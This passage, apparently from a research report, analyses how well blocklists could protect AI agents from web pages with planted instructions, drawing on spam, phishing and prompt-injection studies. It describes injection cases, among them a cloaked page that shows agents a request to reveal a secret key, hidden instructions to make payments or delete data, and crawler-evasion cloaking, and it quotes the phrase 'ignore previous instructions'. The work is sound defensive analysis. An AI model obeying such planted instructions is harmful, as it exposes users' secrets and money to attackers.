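A blocklist can't stop an attacker from buying new domains, but it can make them a bad investment. Let v be the value to the attacker of one deceived visit, r the number of deceived visits per hour, T the number of hours until the list catches the source, and c the cost of a new source. Each source earns v·r·T before the list catches it, so source rotation pays while

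v·r·T > c.

Dividing both sides by T gives v·r > c/T, so a blocklist in effect adds an hourly cost of c/T to the attack. If a domain costs ten dollars and lasts 24 hours, that cost is about 42 cents an hour.

To illustrate the condition with invented figures, suppose a site earns five cents from each agent it deceives, perhaps as a commission on a camera, and deceives 20 agents an hour. It earns a dollar an hour, so a ten-dollar domain has to last at least ten hours to recover its cost.

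| Situation | Earned before listing | Cost of source | Result per source |
|---|---|---|---|
| Listed after 24 hours | $24.00 | $10 | $14.00 gain |
| Listed after 1 hour | $1.00 | $10 | $9.00 loss |
| Listed after 24 hours, source costs $50 | $24.00 | $50 | $26.00 loss |
| Listed after 24 hours, 95% of agents refuse new domains | $1.20 | $10 | $8.80 loss |
| Listed after 24 hours, free address on a shared site | $24.00 | $0 | $24.00 gain |

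Listing the site faster, raising the price of a domain and distrusting new domains can each turn the attacker's gain into a loss. But an improvement too small to make rotation unprofitable may protect no agents. If T falls from 24 hours to 12, rotation is still profitable, and an attacker with the next domain ready continues to deceive 20 agents an hour at a lower profit.

How well default distrust works also depends on how a source stops being new. If a filter refuses domains less than a month old, an attacker can register a hundred today and wait a month. All of them will then pass the age check, so the attacker can replace any that get blocked, having only had to wait and pay the registration fees in advance. A rule that required a record of real use would be harder to get around.

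The condition is most useful against attacks that earn a little from each of many victims. If one successful deception yields a company password worth $1,000, an attacker who pays $10 per domain breaks even with one success per hundred domains. Blocklists are unlikely to deter that attacker, although they may stop some attempts.

For agents, c may be much higher than the price of a domain, because an agent that finds pages by searching won't open a site that ranks on the tenth page of results. If it takes $500 of work to get each new site noticed, the example site would have to survive for 500 hours. This greatly reduces the filtering needed, but only against attackers who rely on search. Someone who emails a link to the agent or writes a review on an established store avoids this cost.

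T could also be close to zero. A company that runs millions of agents might detect an attack on one of them and block the source for all the others within minutes, much faster than people report phishing. However, T includes the time before anyone notices the attack, and nobody else has a chance to see an attack on a single company.

### Rare attacks and false alarms

Finding hostile sources quickly usually means flagging them automatically, which causes trouble when almost every source is harmless. Stefan Axelsson made this argument in 1999 about intrusion detection, the automated search for break-ins on computer systems. When break-ins are very rare, even a low false-alarm rate produces far more false alarms than real ones.

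Khodayari and colleagues searched the public web by keyword and confirmed hostile or bot-directed instructions on 285 of 24.8 million hosts, or about one in 87,000. A filter that judged all 24.8 million hosts and caught 90% of the 285 would catch about 257. How far a user could trust its flags would depend mostly on how often it flagged harmless hosts.

| Harmless hosts wrongly flagged | Number wrongly flagged | Share of flags that are right |
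|---|---|---|
| 1% | about 248,000 | about 1 in 1,000 |
| 0.01% | about 2,480 | about 1 in 11 |
| 0.001% | about 248 | about 1 in 2 |

Catching all 285 hosts instead of 257 would hardly help, because at a false positive rate of 1%, only about one flag in 870 would be right. Checking the 248,000 flagged hosts by hand, at one minute each, would take about 4,100 hours, or two years of full-time work.

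The researchers' own search shows the same effect. Their keywords matched text on 999 hosts, and manual checks confirmed 285 of them. The other 714 were about 0.003% of the harmless hosts, but they made up 71% of the matches.

The count of 285 hosts is a lower bound, because a keyword search misses instructions that are worded unexpectedly. If the true number were a hundred times higher, about one in eleven flags from a filter with a 1% false positive rate would be correct, which is better but still poor. However, some of the 285 hosts carried text meant to keep bots from copying their content, and a user might not want to block those.

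The rate per host also differs from the rate per visit, because agents don't choose hosts at random. If they mostly visit large, well-run sites, they may meet hostile instructions less often than one host in 87,000 suggests. If attackers push their pages up the results for popular shopping queries, agents may meet such instructions far more often, and a flag on one of those pages is more likely to be correct. A filter's designers need the rate among the pages that agents open, which the host count doesn't provide.

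### How small errors add up

A person who finds one site blocked can usually try another. An agent may consult dozens of sources for a single task, so even a low error rate affects many tasks. Suppose a filter wrongly blocks 0.5% of useful sources and a task needs 50 of them. If the errors are independent, the chance that none are blocked is 0.995^50, or about 78%, so the task loses at least one source about 22% of the time. With 200 sources, the chance of losing at least one rises to 63%.

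Real errors probably cluster, because a filter that blocks one small forum on a shared server may also block its neighbours. Suppose all the wrongful blocks fall on a tenth of tasks, such as those about niche hobbies, and the filter blocks 5% of the useful sources for those tasks. The overall rate is still 0.5%, but now only about 9% of all tasks lose at least one useful source. Within the affected tenth, 92% do, and they lose two or three on average. An overall error rate would not show how badly the filter serves those users.

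Distrusting new domains makes this worse. If 2% of the useful sources for a task are new and the filter blocks them all, a task that needs 50 sources loses at least one about 64% of the time. The loss matters less if another site has the same information, but a new site is sometimes the only one that covers a new product.

Missed attacks add up in the same way. If one visit in 10,000 leads to a hostile page and the filter catches 90% of these pages, a task with 50 visits has a 0.05% chance of reaching one. Over 1,000 such tasks, the chance of reaching at least one is 39%, compared with more than 99% without the filter.

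## Measurements of spam and phishing lists: coverage, delay and rotation

Rotating sources stops helping attackers once lists catch each new source quickly enough, so the speed of real lists matters. Researchers have monitored live lists since the early 2000s, usually measuring coverage, which is the share of hostile sources or messages a list catches, and delay, which is the time from a source's first appearance to its listing. The email measurements in this section are old, dating from 2004 to 2008, but the later phishing measurements found some of the same weaknesses.

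### Email lists from 2004 to 2008

*Blacklists Compared* (2004), a survey from the San Diego Supercomputer Center, looked up 25,311 connecting IP addresses on all known public lists. The largest list contained 47% of them, and most of the lists together contained 72%. The survey didn't separate spammers from legitimate senders, so neither figure measures how much spam the lists caught.

To measure how much spam these lists cover, Ramachandran and Feamster, in *Understanding the Network-Level Behavior of Spammers*, registered a domain with no legitimate email addresses, so all the mail it received was spam. It received more than 10 million messages between August 2004 and the start of 2006. As each message arrived, their server looked up the sender on eight lists. About 80% of the spam came from an address on at least one list, but SpamCop, the list with the best coverage, contained the senders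 of only about half.

An earlier study by Jung and Sit also found 80%, but it checked the spammers' addresses two months after recording the traffic. Its count could therefore include addresses that were listed long after the spam was delivered, whereas a mail server has to decide within seconds.

A domain that gets only spam can't show how much legitimate mail a list would block. In *Shades of Grey*, Sinha, Bailey and Jahanian measured both missed spam and wrongly flagged legitimate mail on a working academic network of about 7,000 machines. They recorded just over a million delivered messages over ten days in June 2008 and looked up the senders on four lists. To decide which messages were spam, they used the content filter SpamAssassin, which classified about 80% as spam.

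| List | Spam missed | Legitimate messages wrongly flagged | Legitimate senders wrongly flagged |
|---|---|---|---|
| NJABL | 98.4% | 0.2% | 0.5% |
| SORBS | 64.8% | 9.5% | 26.9% |
| SpamCop | 34.9% | 2.3% | 13.6% |
| Spamhaus | 36.3% | 0.6% | 5.2% |

The last two columns differ so much because ten machines sent 80% of the legitimate mail, and most lists did not list the big senders. The exception was SORBS, which had listed six of Google's mail servers. The errors therefore fell mainly on small senders. A web filter that rarely blocks big sites could likewise have a much lower error rate per page visit than per site.

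SpamCop alone caught 65% of the spam, adding Spamhaus raised this to 72%, and adding SORBS raised it to 79%. The three lists together missed 21% of the spam, but would have missed only about 8% if they had missed spam independently of each other. Sinha and colleagues suggest that the lists' spamtraps may have overlapped too much to catch the rest.

SpamCop and Spamhaus together flagged 2.9% of legitimate messages, and adding the third list, SORBS, raised this to 11.4%. With SORBS added, a server that rejected mail on any match would have caught 7 percentage points more spam but lost 8.5 points more legitimate mail.

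These figures depend on SpamAssassin's accuracy. On four mailboxes that people had sorted by hand, it missed 4% to 6% of the spam and wrongly flagged at most about 0.6% of legitimate mail. A bigger concern is that SpamAssassin can look up senders on blocklists. If it did so in this study, its verdicts partly depended on the lists it was used to test, and the lists probably performed worse than measured.

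### Threat feeds for companies

Companies also buy or download threat intelligence feeds, which Li, Dunn and colleagues' *Reading the Tea Leaves* describes as up-to-date compilations of known threats, such as IP addresses, domain names and file hashes. Subscribing to more than one feed would be an obvious way to improve coverage.

*A different cup of TI*, a 2020 study of paid feeds, found that few entries appeared in more than one vendor's feed. Shared entries reached the second feed an average of a month after the first, by which time many phishing sites would be gone. The low overlap may mean that each vendor covers a different part of the threat, in which case buying both feeds makes sense, or that both see only a small part of a much larger threat.

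Buyers of paid feeds cared more about saving their analysts' time than about detecting as many threats as possible, according to interviews with 14 security professionals who used such feeds. That priority may be reasonable for a company whose analysts investigate each alert, but an agent's filter must block or admit a page without an analyst, so it needs the coverage these buyers were willing to do without.

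### How spammers moved between addresses

Much of the spam that lists missed came from botnets, networks of infected computers under one attacker's control. Ramachandran and Feamster had a record of 117,268 machines infected with the Bobax worm, and 4,693 of them sent spam to the test domain. More than 65% of these sent spam only once, and about three-quarters were active for less than two minutes. Over the 17 months, 99% sent the domain fewer than 100 messages.

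Sinha and colleagues also found that most unlisted spam sources sent few messages. Of 67,442 machines outside the network that sent spam and were on none of the lists, only 100 sent 20 or more messages. At least 80% of the 67,442 were seen on the network for just one second. A single mail server would have almost no data of its own for judging such a sender.

Ramachandran and Feamster therefore expected lists to do badly against bots, but the Bobax machines were more likely to be listed than the average spammer. A machine that sent one message to their domain had probably sent many to other domains, and a shared list could combine those sightings. Similarly, agents that report to a shared list could get a hostile page listed even if each agent opens it only once, as long as some of them notice the attack.

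A more sophisticated group of spammers announced to the internet's routers that a block of addresses belonged to them, sent spam from unused addresses inside it, and withdrew the announcement soon afterwards. On 30 September 2005, for example, spam arrived from a block of 16.8 million addresses that was reachable only briefly. Half of the addresses used this way were on none of the eight lists. The technique never accounted for more than about 10% of the spam at the test domain, but it gave spammers an almost unlimited supply of new addresses.

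List operators can respond to rotation by making each entry cover more addresses, so that the attacker's next address is already on the list. Ramachandran and Feamster received 36% of their spam from twenty networks, and they suggest in their technical report listing ranges instead of single addresses. Other researchers proposed listing the ranges that internet providers assign temporarily to customers, because mail from these was mostly spam. Listing a range risks blocking innocent senders in it. Most legitimate mail came from the same broad regions of the address space as the spam, so a range has to be fairly narrow to separate the two.

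Attackers who run websites also rotate IP addresses and domain names. In fast flux, they keep changing a domain's DNS record so that the same name leads to one infected machine after another. This defeats a list of IP addresses, but a list that names the domain still works. To get around domain lists, some malware uses a formula to generate a long series of domain names, often from the date. The attacker uses the same formula and registers a few of the names, and the malware tries names from the series until one responds. Defenders who work out the formula can list the names in advance.

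Machine-generated domain names are probably not much use for misleading agents, because an agent can't calculate each new name and would have to find it through a search, a link or a message.

### Phishing on free hosts

According to *From Past to Present*, a survey by Tian, Yu and colleagues (2025), blocklists are still the most common way to detect malicious web addresses, and they have few false positives but cannot recognise new addresses. How much they miss seems to depend heavily on where the attacker hosts the page.

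Saha Roy, Karanjit and Nilizadeh (2023), in *A Large-Scale Analysis of Phishing Websites Hosted on Free Web Hosting Domains*, collected links from Twitter and Facebook for six months from November 2022. They used a machine-learning classifier to find 31,405 phishing pages made with 17 free website builders, such as Weebly and Wix, and a similar classifier to find the same number on attackers' own domains. They then checked every ten minutes whether each page was on four lists. They did not report the pages to the lists' operators, who had to learn about them some other way. The table gives each list's coverage within a week and its median delay.

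| List | Attackers' own domains | Free hosts |
|---|---|---|
| Google Safe Browsing | 74.2%, 51 minutes | 18.4%, 6 hours |
| APWG eCrimeX | 47.9%, 4.4 hours | 32.9%, 8.9 hours |
| OpenPhish | 30.5%, 2.4 hours | 11.7%, 13.3 hours |
| PhishTank | 17.4%, 2.5 hours | 4.1%, 7.2 hours |

The median delays include only pages that the list eventually caught. Safe Browsing's median delay on free hosts was six hours, so after six hours it had listed about 9% of all pages there, not half.

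Medians also don't reflect the pages that last longest, which matter most to an attacker deciding whether to buy another domain. The median time to listing was 51 minutes among listed pages on attackers' own domains, but about 26% of the pages on those domains stayed off Safe Browsing for the whole week. Counting each of those as just one week makes the average time to listing at least 43 hours. However, hosting companies removed 77.5% of the pages on attackers' own domains, typically within four hours, so some of the pages that Safe Browsing did not list had probably disappeared before it needed to list them.

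The exact size of the gap in coverage between free hosts and other domains is uncertain because the paper's figures are inconsistent. A separate breakdown gives Safe Browsing's coverage for each free host, including 60% for Weebly and 68% for 000webhost. The average across all the hosts in that breakdown, weighted by the number of pages on each, is about 45%, not 18.4%. The text also gives 24-hour coverage as 31% for free hosts and 83% for attackers' own domains, both higher than the table's figures for a whole week. But even 45% is far below 74.2%, and all four lists did worse on free hosts.

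The classifier might also have mistaken some harmless pages for phishing. On a test set that was half phishing, about 4% of the pages it flagged were harmless. If only a tenth of the pages in the live stream were phishing, that share would rise to about 27%. Saha Roy and colleagues mention that a page was included only if at least two security tools detected it. This rule would remove many of these mistakes, but it would also remove real phishing pages that every tool missed, and so make the lists look better than they are.

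### Why shared hosts are hard to list

Blocking the whole domain of a free web host such as Wix would block every other customer's site too. A list operator therefore has to find and list each hostile site separately, and the attacker can replace each one for free.

Phishing pages on free hosts also lack the usual warning signs. Many detectors treat new domains as suspicious, but a page on Weebly or Google Sites has the age of the host's domain. In a sample of 4,656 phishing pages from free hosts, the median domain age was 13.7 years, compared with 71 days for the same number of pages on attackers' own domains. About 89% of the sample also had a .com address, which attackers otherwise tend to avoid because it costs more. Harmless and hostile customers use the same templates, so their pages have similar code, with a median similarity of 79.4% on Weebly.

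If these ages were recorded at the time of the attacks, a list of domains registered in the previous 30 days would have missed more than half of the phishing pages on attackers' own domains and nearly all of those on free hosts.

Pages on free hosts are also harder to find. When a website gets its own security certificate, the certificate appears in a public log, which many phishing detectors check for suspicious names. A page on a free host uses the host's certificate, so it creates no new entry. Crawlers that start from search results are likely to miss most of these pages too. Of the free-host phishing pages in the researchers' earlier collection, Google had indexed only 4.1%, and nearly 45% carried a tag meant to keep them out of search results.

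Attackers who rely on search to reach agents can't hide their pages from Google, because agents searching Google wouldn't find those pages either. This should make such attacks easier for list operators to find than phishing links in social media posts.

Some phishing pages on free hosts contain nothing obviously hostile. About 24% of those on Google Sites had only a button that led to the real phishing page on another domain. A list might block the second page but not the first, which the attacker can then link to a new phishing page.

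The most direct remedy is for the host to remove the page, but hosts vary widely in how many reported pages they remove. After receiving the researchers' reports, Wix removed 65% of the phishing pages and Weebly 59%, both with median times of around two hours. Google Sites removed 8% and WordPress 5%. A free host's record of removing abuse might therefore be more informative to an agent than the age or popularity of its domain.

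### Delays on Twitter

A few large campaigns can dominate a measurement of delay. Bell, Paterson and Cavallaro (2019), in *Catch Me (On Time) If You Can*, followed links on Twitter in October and November 2017 and recorded when each appeared in Safe Browsing. Safe Browsing labelled 3,273 of the links first tweeted in October as phishing or similar deception within a month before or after the tweet. Most of these took 18 to 26 days to get listed.

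But seven domains supplied 76% of the links. Without them, most of the remaining links were listed within six hours. The full-sample result shows how long a typical hostile link in the sample went without a warning, while the result without those seven domains is closer to the performance against a typical hostile domain.

Bell and colleagues could calculate a delay only for links that Safe Browsing listed within a month. Their comparison leaves out links that it listed later or never listed, so the true delays were probably longer.

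More recent work suggests that the problem continued. For *PhishLang*, Saha Roy and Nilizadeh (2024) ran a new detector on live web addresses from September 2023 to January 2024 and found 25,796 phishing sites. They report that blocklists and hosting companies had lower coverage of these sites, especially those using evasive techniques, and that their own reports helped bring down 74% of them. They took the addresses from the public certificate log, so the sample probably contains few pages on free hosts, where coverage seems to be worst.

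### Planted pages

Researchers can avoid some of these problems by planting their own test pages, because they then know exactly when each page appeared. Saha Roy and colleagues say that an earlier project of this kind, PhishTime by Oest and colleagues, found that including evidence such as screenshots in a report speeds up the response.

In *PhishClone*, Wong, Almashor and colleagues (2022) put seven copies of PayPal's login page online with the company's permission. They made each copy with a different technique they had found in real phishing pages, ranging from reusing the original code to rebuilding the page with a website builder. For a week, they submitted the pages every half hour to VirusTotal, a service that collects verdicts from dozens of security tools, and also checked Safe Browsing and another scanner, Sucuri. None of these services flagged any of the pages.

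It's hard to say what caused this result. For ethical reasons, the pages collected no data, had random addresses and received no visitors. A detector that looks for stolen passwords leaving the page therefore had nothing to find, and there were no visitors to report the pages. All seven were also on shared hosting services, six on Netlify and one on Wix, so the scanners may have missed them for that reason rather than because of the copying techniques. Testing the same pages on newly registered domains would help separate these explanations.

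Planted injection pages would raise a similar difficulty. A test page with harmless instructions may not deserve a listing, while one with harmful instructions could hurt a real user whose agent found it.

### Pages that crawlers don't see

A phishing site that uses cloaking against a list's crawlers checks each visitor's IP address, user agent (the text a browser sends to identify itself) and other details of the request. The site shows the phishing page to visitors who look like potential victims, but if a visitor looks like a security company, it shows an error message or redirects them to the website of the company it impersonates.

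Most phishing kits, ready-made packages for setting up a phishing site, include cloaking code. *PhishParrot* (Nakano, Koide and Chiba, 2025) cites a study by Zhang and colleagues that found it in 2,831 of 2,933 kits (96.5%). Of 2,421 kits examined in more detail, 82% checked the visitor's user agent and 69% checked the IP address.

Another study they cite examined 112,005 live phishing sites in 2018 and 2019 and found that the share using cloaking rose from 23% to 34%. This is much lower than the figure for kits, but it covers only cloaking code that runs in the visitor's browser and misses checks on the attacker's server, which can't be seen from outside. A kit may also include cloaking code that its buyer never switches on. The share of live sites that hide from crawlers is therefore uncertain, but it's clearly large enough to affect any list that relies on crawlers.

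Crawlers can fight back by disguising themselves. Nakano and colleagues built one that works as follows.

1. It makes an ordinary visit and records the domain's registration, the network traffic and the page's code.
2. It searches a database for similar phishing sites and retrieves examples of visits that reached the hidden page and visits that failed.
3. It gives these examples to a language model, which suggests what kind of visitor the attacker wants, including the country, the type of network and the browser settings.
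4. It visits again with those settings and passes the result to a phishing detector.

In a 21-day test on 32,487 suspicious addresses, the best version was 88.0% accurate and took 16.7 seconds per address. Nakano and colleagues report that the disguise improved detection by up to 33.8% compared with a standard crawler visiting from a cloud server in the United States. The 33.8% figure is the best result among three detectors.

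Disguised crawling is slow but feasible. At 16.7 seconds per host, crawling the 24.8 million hosts in the survey by Khodayari and colleagues would take about 13 years on one machine, or five days on a thousand. Keeping the results up to date would require repeated crawls, because a site can change immediately after each one.

### Pages that only agents see

Websites can recognise agents more easily than a particular kind of human victim. Browser automation software often sets a flag that the site can read. Agents may also connect from data centres, fill in forms instantly or fail to move the mouse as a person would. Some companies, including OpenAI, publish details that identify their agents.

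Zychlinski (2025), in *A Whole New World*, used this to build a test site with two versions of the same documentation page. Ordinary visitors saw harmless documentation. Agents saw instructions to authenticate first by supplying a secret key stored on the user's computer, and the command for reading that key. The attack worked on the coding agent Cursor with all three models tested, Claude 4 Sonnet, GPT-5 Fast and Gemini 2.5 Pro.

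The paper doesn't say how many times each model was tested, and the companies have since released newer models, so its results aren't good evidence of how often current agents would reveal the key. A better model might refuse the request, but the site could still show it a page that nobody else sees, because switching pages doesn't depend on the model.

A crawler that builds a reputation list gets the harmless page if it identifies itself as a crawler or looks like an ordinary browser, so it records the site as clean. User reports don't help much, because an employee who checks the page also sees the harmless version and may dismiss the report. The site can then build up a good record while attacking every agent that visits. This is a prediction from the design, since Zychlinski didn't send any security crawlers to the test site, but phishing kits already treat crawlers this way.

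Zychlinski suggests that agents vary their browser details to blend in with human visitors, and that security companies send out decoy agents to report sites that ask for data they shouldn't have. Decoys seem especially promising for companies that run agents themselves. If a decoy uses the same software and IP addresses as the real agents, an attacker can't avoid it without also avoiding the real agents.

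The attacker can still slow detection by showing the hostile page only some of the time. If each visit has a 10% chance of getting the hostile version, 20 decoy visits have an 88% chance of finding it at least once. The attacker also loses nine-tenths of the possible victims, but this matters less if they need only one company's password.

### What nobody has counted

Comparing two lists might give an estimate of how many hostile sources both have missed. Biologists use this method to count animals. They catch some, mark and release them, then catch a second group. If most of the second group are marked, there are probably few animals left to find.

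In the 2008 email data, this method greatly underestimated how much spam both lists missed. Out of every 1,000 spam messages, Spamhaus caught 636, SpamCop caught 650, and both caught 565. If the lists had worked independently, this overlap would imply a total of 636 × 650 / 565, or about 732 messages. Together the lists caught 721, which would mean they missed only about 11, but they actually missed 279. They tended to catch and miss the same messages, so their overlap made their coverage look almost complete.

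Sinha and colleagues could identify the spam that the lists missed only because they had all the network's mail and a fairly accurate filter to sort it. Nobody has all the pages that agents open, and sorting them is difficult because keyword searches for injected instructions mostly find harmless text. Two lists of sites that attack agents could therefore overlap heavily and still miss most of the attacks.

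The phishing figures are a poor substitute for measurements of injection pages, because phishing detectors rely on features that an injection page doesn't need. For example, Saha Roy and colleagues confirmed their first sample by checking whether pages imitated one of 409 well-known brands and whether they asked for sensitive information. A fake camera review with a hidden instruction does neither. About 14% of the phishing pages on free hosts had no fields for passwords or other personal details. Several hosts where such pages were common, including Google Sites, Blogspot and SharePoint, had some of the lowest coverage. Those hosts were also slow to remove pages, so the missing fields may not be the main reason for the low coverage, but coverage of pages written for agents could easily be even lower.

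Lists built for agents could also do better than phishing lists, because the company that runs an agent can see everything the agent does after opening a page. Operators of phishing lists rarely see a victim type in a password, but if an agent reads a camera review and then tries to open the user's email, the company has a record of both actions. By checking such records automatically, the company could list a hostile page without waiting for a person to report it.

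## Surveys of hostile instructions on the web

A blocklist for agents would have to include the sites that carry text aimed at agents. Several groups searched the web for such text in 2025 and 2026. They recorded where the text was and often who had put it there, which is enough to estimate what a reputation filter could have caught, although they were not testing such filters.

### The April 2026 crawl

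Khodayari and colleagues published the largest survey in April 2026. They searched about half of the October 2025 edition of Common Crawl, a public archive of web pages, for 3,963 phrases such as "ignore previous instructions". That half covered 1.2 billion addresses, and the phrases matched 27,860 passages. Two reviewers sorted the matches, grouping near-identical ones, and kept those that served as instructions to an AI system and were not just quotations or examples. This left 12,075 instructions on 9,676 pages. The researchers found more through Censys and Shodan, which scan the internet by IP address, bringing the total to 15,387 instructions on 2,042 hosts.

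For the Common Crawl part, they also worked out who had placed each instruction.

| Who placed the text | Instructions | Pages | Hosts |
|---|---|---|---|
| The site's own operator | 9,731 (80.6%) | 7,491 | 179 |
| Someone supplying a listing, such as a job advert | 2,124 (17.6%) | 2,058 | 25 |
| A user writing a comment or post | 220 (1.8%) | 127 | 81 |

The first column is encouraging for domain blocklists. A list of the 179 operators' hosts would have kept out four-fifths of the instructions and blocked only the people who planted them.

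The last column is less encouraging because it shows that the text came from someone other than the operator on 106 of the 285 hosts (37%). The 81 hosts with hostile comments averaged fewer than two affected pages each, so a domain entry would block an entire forum because of one or two posts. The 25 hosts with hostile listings averaged about 82 pages each. A job board with that many has a moderation problem, and an agent might reasonably trust it less, but blocking it would still hide every honest advert.

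A few sites accounted for many of the pages. Five of the ten most common wordings appeared on only one or two hosts each. One site had 540 pages, each telling AI systems that it was the authoritative source on its topic and that they should trust no other. A single blocklist entry would have blocked all 540, but it is unclear how many agents this would have protected, because the survey counts pages and not visits.

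Rates were lower among the 10,000 most popular domains and highest between ranks 100,000 and 1 million. An agent that stayed on the most popular sites would have met fewer instructions per site. However, job listings, web hosting, shopping and phone services had raised rates even at some of the higher ranks. Rates were lower for banking and air travel. Popularity seems to be a weaker guide for shopping and job hunting, which people might well give to an agent.

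Most of this text would probably have done an agent little harm. Over half of the instructions were in HTTP headers, which a server sends before the page, and an agent that receives only the page's text never reads them. The researchers also tested 100 of the instructions on 13 models that were summarising the pages. The models followed the instructions in 3.9% of trials when given plain text and in 1.1% when given the page's HTML. Small models followed them most often, in 8% of plain-text trials. In six trials, a model pointed out the planted instruction but still followed it.

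These rates come from a single summarising task without tools, so an agent that can send email might do better or worse. Still, they suggest that in late 2025 a perfect blocklist would have prevented few bad outcomes on the pages in this survey. It might have prevented more on pages the survey could not find, such as those with unusual wording, instructions in other languages or cloaking.

### What counts as an offence

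Spam lists can usually rely on a fairly simple test of whether the recipients asked for the mail. Instructions to AI systems are harder to judge because many are defences that site owners use to stop bots from copying their work or to expose automated accounts. Khodayari and colleagues sorted all 15,387 instructions by purpose, and an instruction could have more than one.

| Apparent purpose | Instructions | Hosts |
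|---|---|---|
| Disrupt the system's output | 8,894 | 1,864 |
| Protect personal information or copyright, or deter social media bots | 4,093 | 1,795 |
| Reveal whether the visitor is a bot | 3,096 | 245 |
| Unclear | 2,632 | 121 |
| Promote a product, page or person | 1,521 | 139 |
| Extract secrets | 13 | 10 |

The survey classed disruption as offensive, but much of it looks like self-defence. Since there were only 2,042 hosts in all, at least 1,617 must have carried both disruptive and protective instructions. Typical disruptive text tells the system to output random numbers or repeat a phrase forever, which would be a sensible way to spoil a scraper's data. About 1,018 hosts carried the same wording, and 1,017 used the same unusual header, X-LLM. These two groups are probably the same hosts, perhaps running software with that text built in.

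The size of a blocklist would depend heavily on which instructions its operator counted as offences. It would include at most 173 of the 2,042 hosts if only promotion, requests for secrets and destructive commands such as deleting a database counted. If any instruction to an AI system counted, all the hosts would be listed, most of them because their owners had told AI systems to keep out of their sites.

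I might seem obvious that the narrower definition is better, but a user can be hurt by a defence too.

 

Google found a page that lured AI visitors to a second page, which sent them an endless stream of text. The site's owner may only have wanted to waste a scraper's resources, but an assistant that opened the page for a reader would get stuck too. Other sites told AI systems to add useful context to their summaries, which Google considered benign.

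Security companies also disagree about the more alarming cases. Unit 42's *Fooling AI Agents*, a March 2026 report from Palo Alto Networks' research group, grades instructions by the damage they would do if an agent obeyed them, and gives its highest grade, critical, to commands to delete files or databases. Google found similar commands but concluded that most were experiments or pranks by individual site owners and had little chance of success. Both views are reasonable, but they lead to different lists. An agent with access to a company's database should probably avoid such a page even if the command was a prank.

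Unit 42 rates a hidden request to print the word "cabbage" five million times as low severity, its grade for instructions it describes as playful, protective or non-malicious. But its published list of indicators, which companies can load into their filters, includes the personal blog post containing the request alongside scam shops and a fake betting site. The list has no severity grades, so a company that blocked everything on it would treat the blog post and the scams alike. Unit 42's own article also carries a notice telling AI agents to treat the page as educational and not to follow its links, so a filter that counted every instruction to an agent as an offence would block the article.

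A list could avoid some of these problems by publishing a reason with each entry, as Spamhaus does with its return codes. A shopping assistant could then refuse sites that plant promotional instructions, and a company's crawler could skip sites that object to copying, without either treating the other group of sites as malicious.

### How long the text stays up

Instructions to AI systems seem to stay online far longer than phishing pages, which hosting companies often remove within hours. Khodayari and colleagues checked the Internet Archive for older copies of the pages they studied. Of the 8,620 pages with a copy from a year earlier, 5,672 (65.8%) already contained such instructions. The share was 77.3% for copies from six months earlier and 93.1% for copies from three months earlier.

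These figures overstate how long a typical instruction lasts, because the researchers started with pages that still had the text in October 2025 and looked backwards. Suppose that every week 100 hostile pages appear that last one week, and one appears that lasts 100 weeks. A snapshot on any day would find about 100 of each kind, so half the pages would be long-lived, even though 99% of hostile pages disappear within a week.

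The survey also checked what happened after the crawl. By January 2026, about three months later, roughly 34% of the instructions in the visible or hidden elements of a page were gone. Some had been in job adverts that had since closed or forms that had changed. This figure can't be compared directly with the 93.1% because it excludes headers, which an operator may set once and forget. It does suggest that turnover is faster than the archive figures imply, though still very slow by the standards of phishing.

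One explanation is that blocklists put little pressure on these sites, although they catch a lot of ordinary abuse. According to Interisle Consulting Group's *Submission of Interisle research report* (2026), security providers had already blocklisted 10% of all domains registered in 2025 under generic endings such as .com. But those providers mostly look for spam, phishing and malware, and about 87% of the instructions in the April 2026 survey were invisible to the human visitors who might have reported them.

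The other explanation is that most of these sites have no need to evade blocking or removal. A publisher that tells bots not to copy its articles has no reason to move to a new domain, and no hosting company would remove the page. The archive figures combine such publishers with people trying to deceive shoppers, so they don't show which explanation is right. Comparing the lifetimes of promotional and protective instructions would help. If the promotional ones also lasted a year, low pressure on deceptive sites would be the more likely reason.

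Even a slowly updated blocklist could catch many of today's pages with hostile instructions. A monthly crawl would be nearly useless against phishing, but it would find a page that stays up for a year. Blocking these pages might make the list less effective over time, because attackers who have never needed to rotate domains can start once their old ones stop working.

### Reports from Google and Unit 42

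Google repeated its scan on several editions of Common Crawl and found 32% more malicious cases in February 2026 than in November 2025. It used Gemini to identify which matching texts seemed out of place on their pages, and people then checked the results. Google gives no absolute numbers, so the rise could be from 50 cases to 66 or from 5,000 to 6,600. The rise could also partly reflect differences in which sites Common Crawl archived.

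Google saw few attempts to steal data and no significant use of the advanced techniques that researchers had published in 2025. But Common Crawl skips sites that require a login or forbid crawling, which excludes most social media. Google said it would study social media separately.

Unit 42 describes twelve cases from its own monitoring data, several of them plainly criminal. A page selling "military glasses" at a fake discount contained 24 hidden attempts to make an AI advertising reviewer approve it. Unit 42 knew of no confirmed case in which such an attempt had fooled a working review system. Another page contained instructions for agents to buy running shoes, and a third contained instructions to send $5,000 through PayPal. The most common aim in the data was irrelevant output (28.6%), followed by data destruction (14.2%) and getting past AI content moderation (9.5%). Unit 42 doesn't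 say how many pages these percentages are based on, and its parent company, Palo Alto Networks, sells products that filter such pages.

A domain blocklist works well against the fake shop, because the whole site exists to deceive, but less well against some of the others. Two of the addresses on Unit 42's list were under pages.dev, a hosting service whose customers share the domain. The payment links led to Stripe and PayPal, which an outbound filter would almost certainly allow. To stop the $5,000 payment by reputation, the filter would need a record of the PayPal account that received it.

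The security company Forcepoint published its findings at about the same time as Google. According to Help Net Security's *Indirect prompt injection is taking hold in the wild*, neither company found sophisticated coordinated campaigns, but Forcepoint thought that identical templates on several domains pointed to "organized tooling". Khodayari's survey also found heavy reuse, with 54 templates making up 95% of the instructions. Bloggers copying a joke from each other would produce the same pattern, so reuse is weak evidence of organisation. Reuse still helps the operators of reputation lists, because once they know a template they can search for every other site that uses it.

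Later in 2026, Zscaler, another security company, documented the two campaigns by impostor sites mentioned at the start, one of them a payment scam. SC Media reports that the researchers traced the culprit to a GitHub account with ten repositories tied to malicious websites. Some of the sites contained instructions for agents to make small payments, for example to settle a copyright dispute. A list that recorded the account could have flagged all the sites together, while a list of domains would have needed an entry for each one.

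### What search services return to coding agents

A newer study starts from searches, so it comes closer than counts of pages or hosts to showing how often an agent meets hostile content. In November 2026, AIR Research Lab, part of the company AIR Security, published a benchmark that sent 4,719 coding queries to eight search services that agents use. According to *Every Major Search API Fed AI Coding Agents Malicious Content, Benchmark Finds* (Faisal, 2026), the lab based the queries on recorded sessions of coding agents fixing real software problems. It fetched each result once as an agent and once as a browser, to catch pages that treat the two differently.

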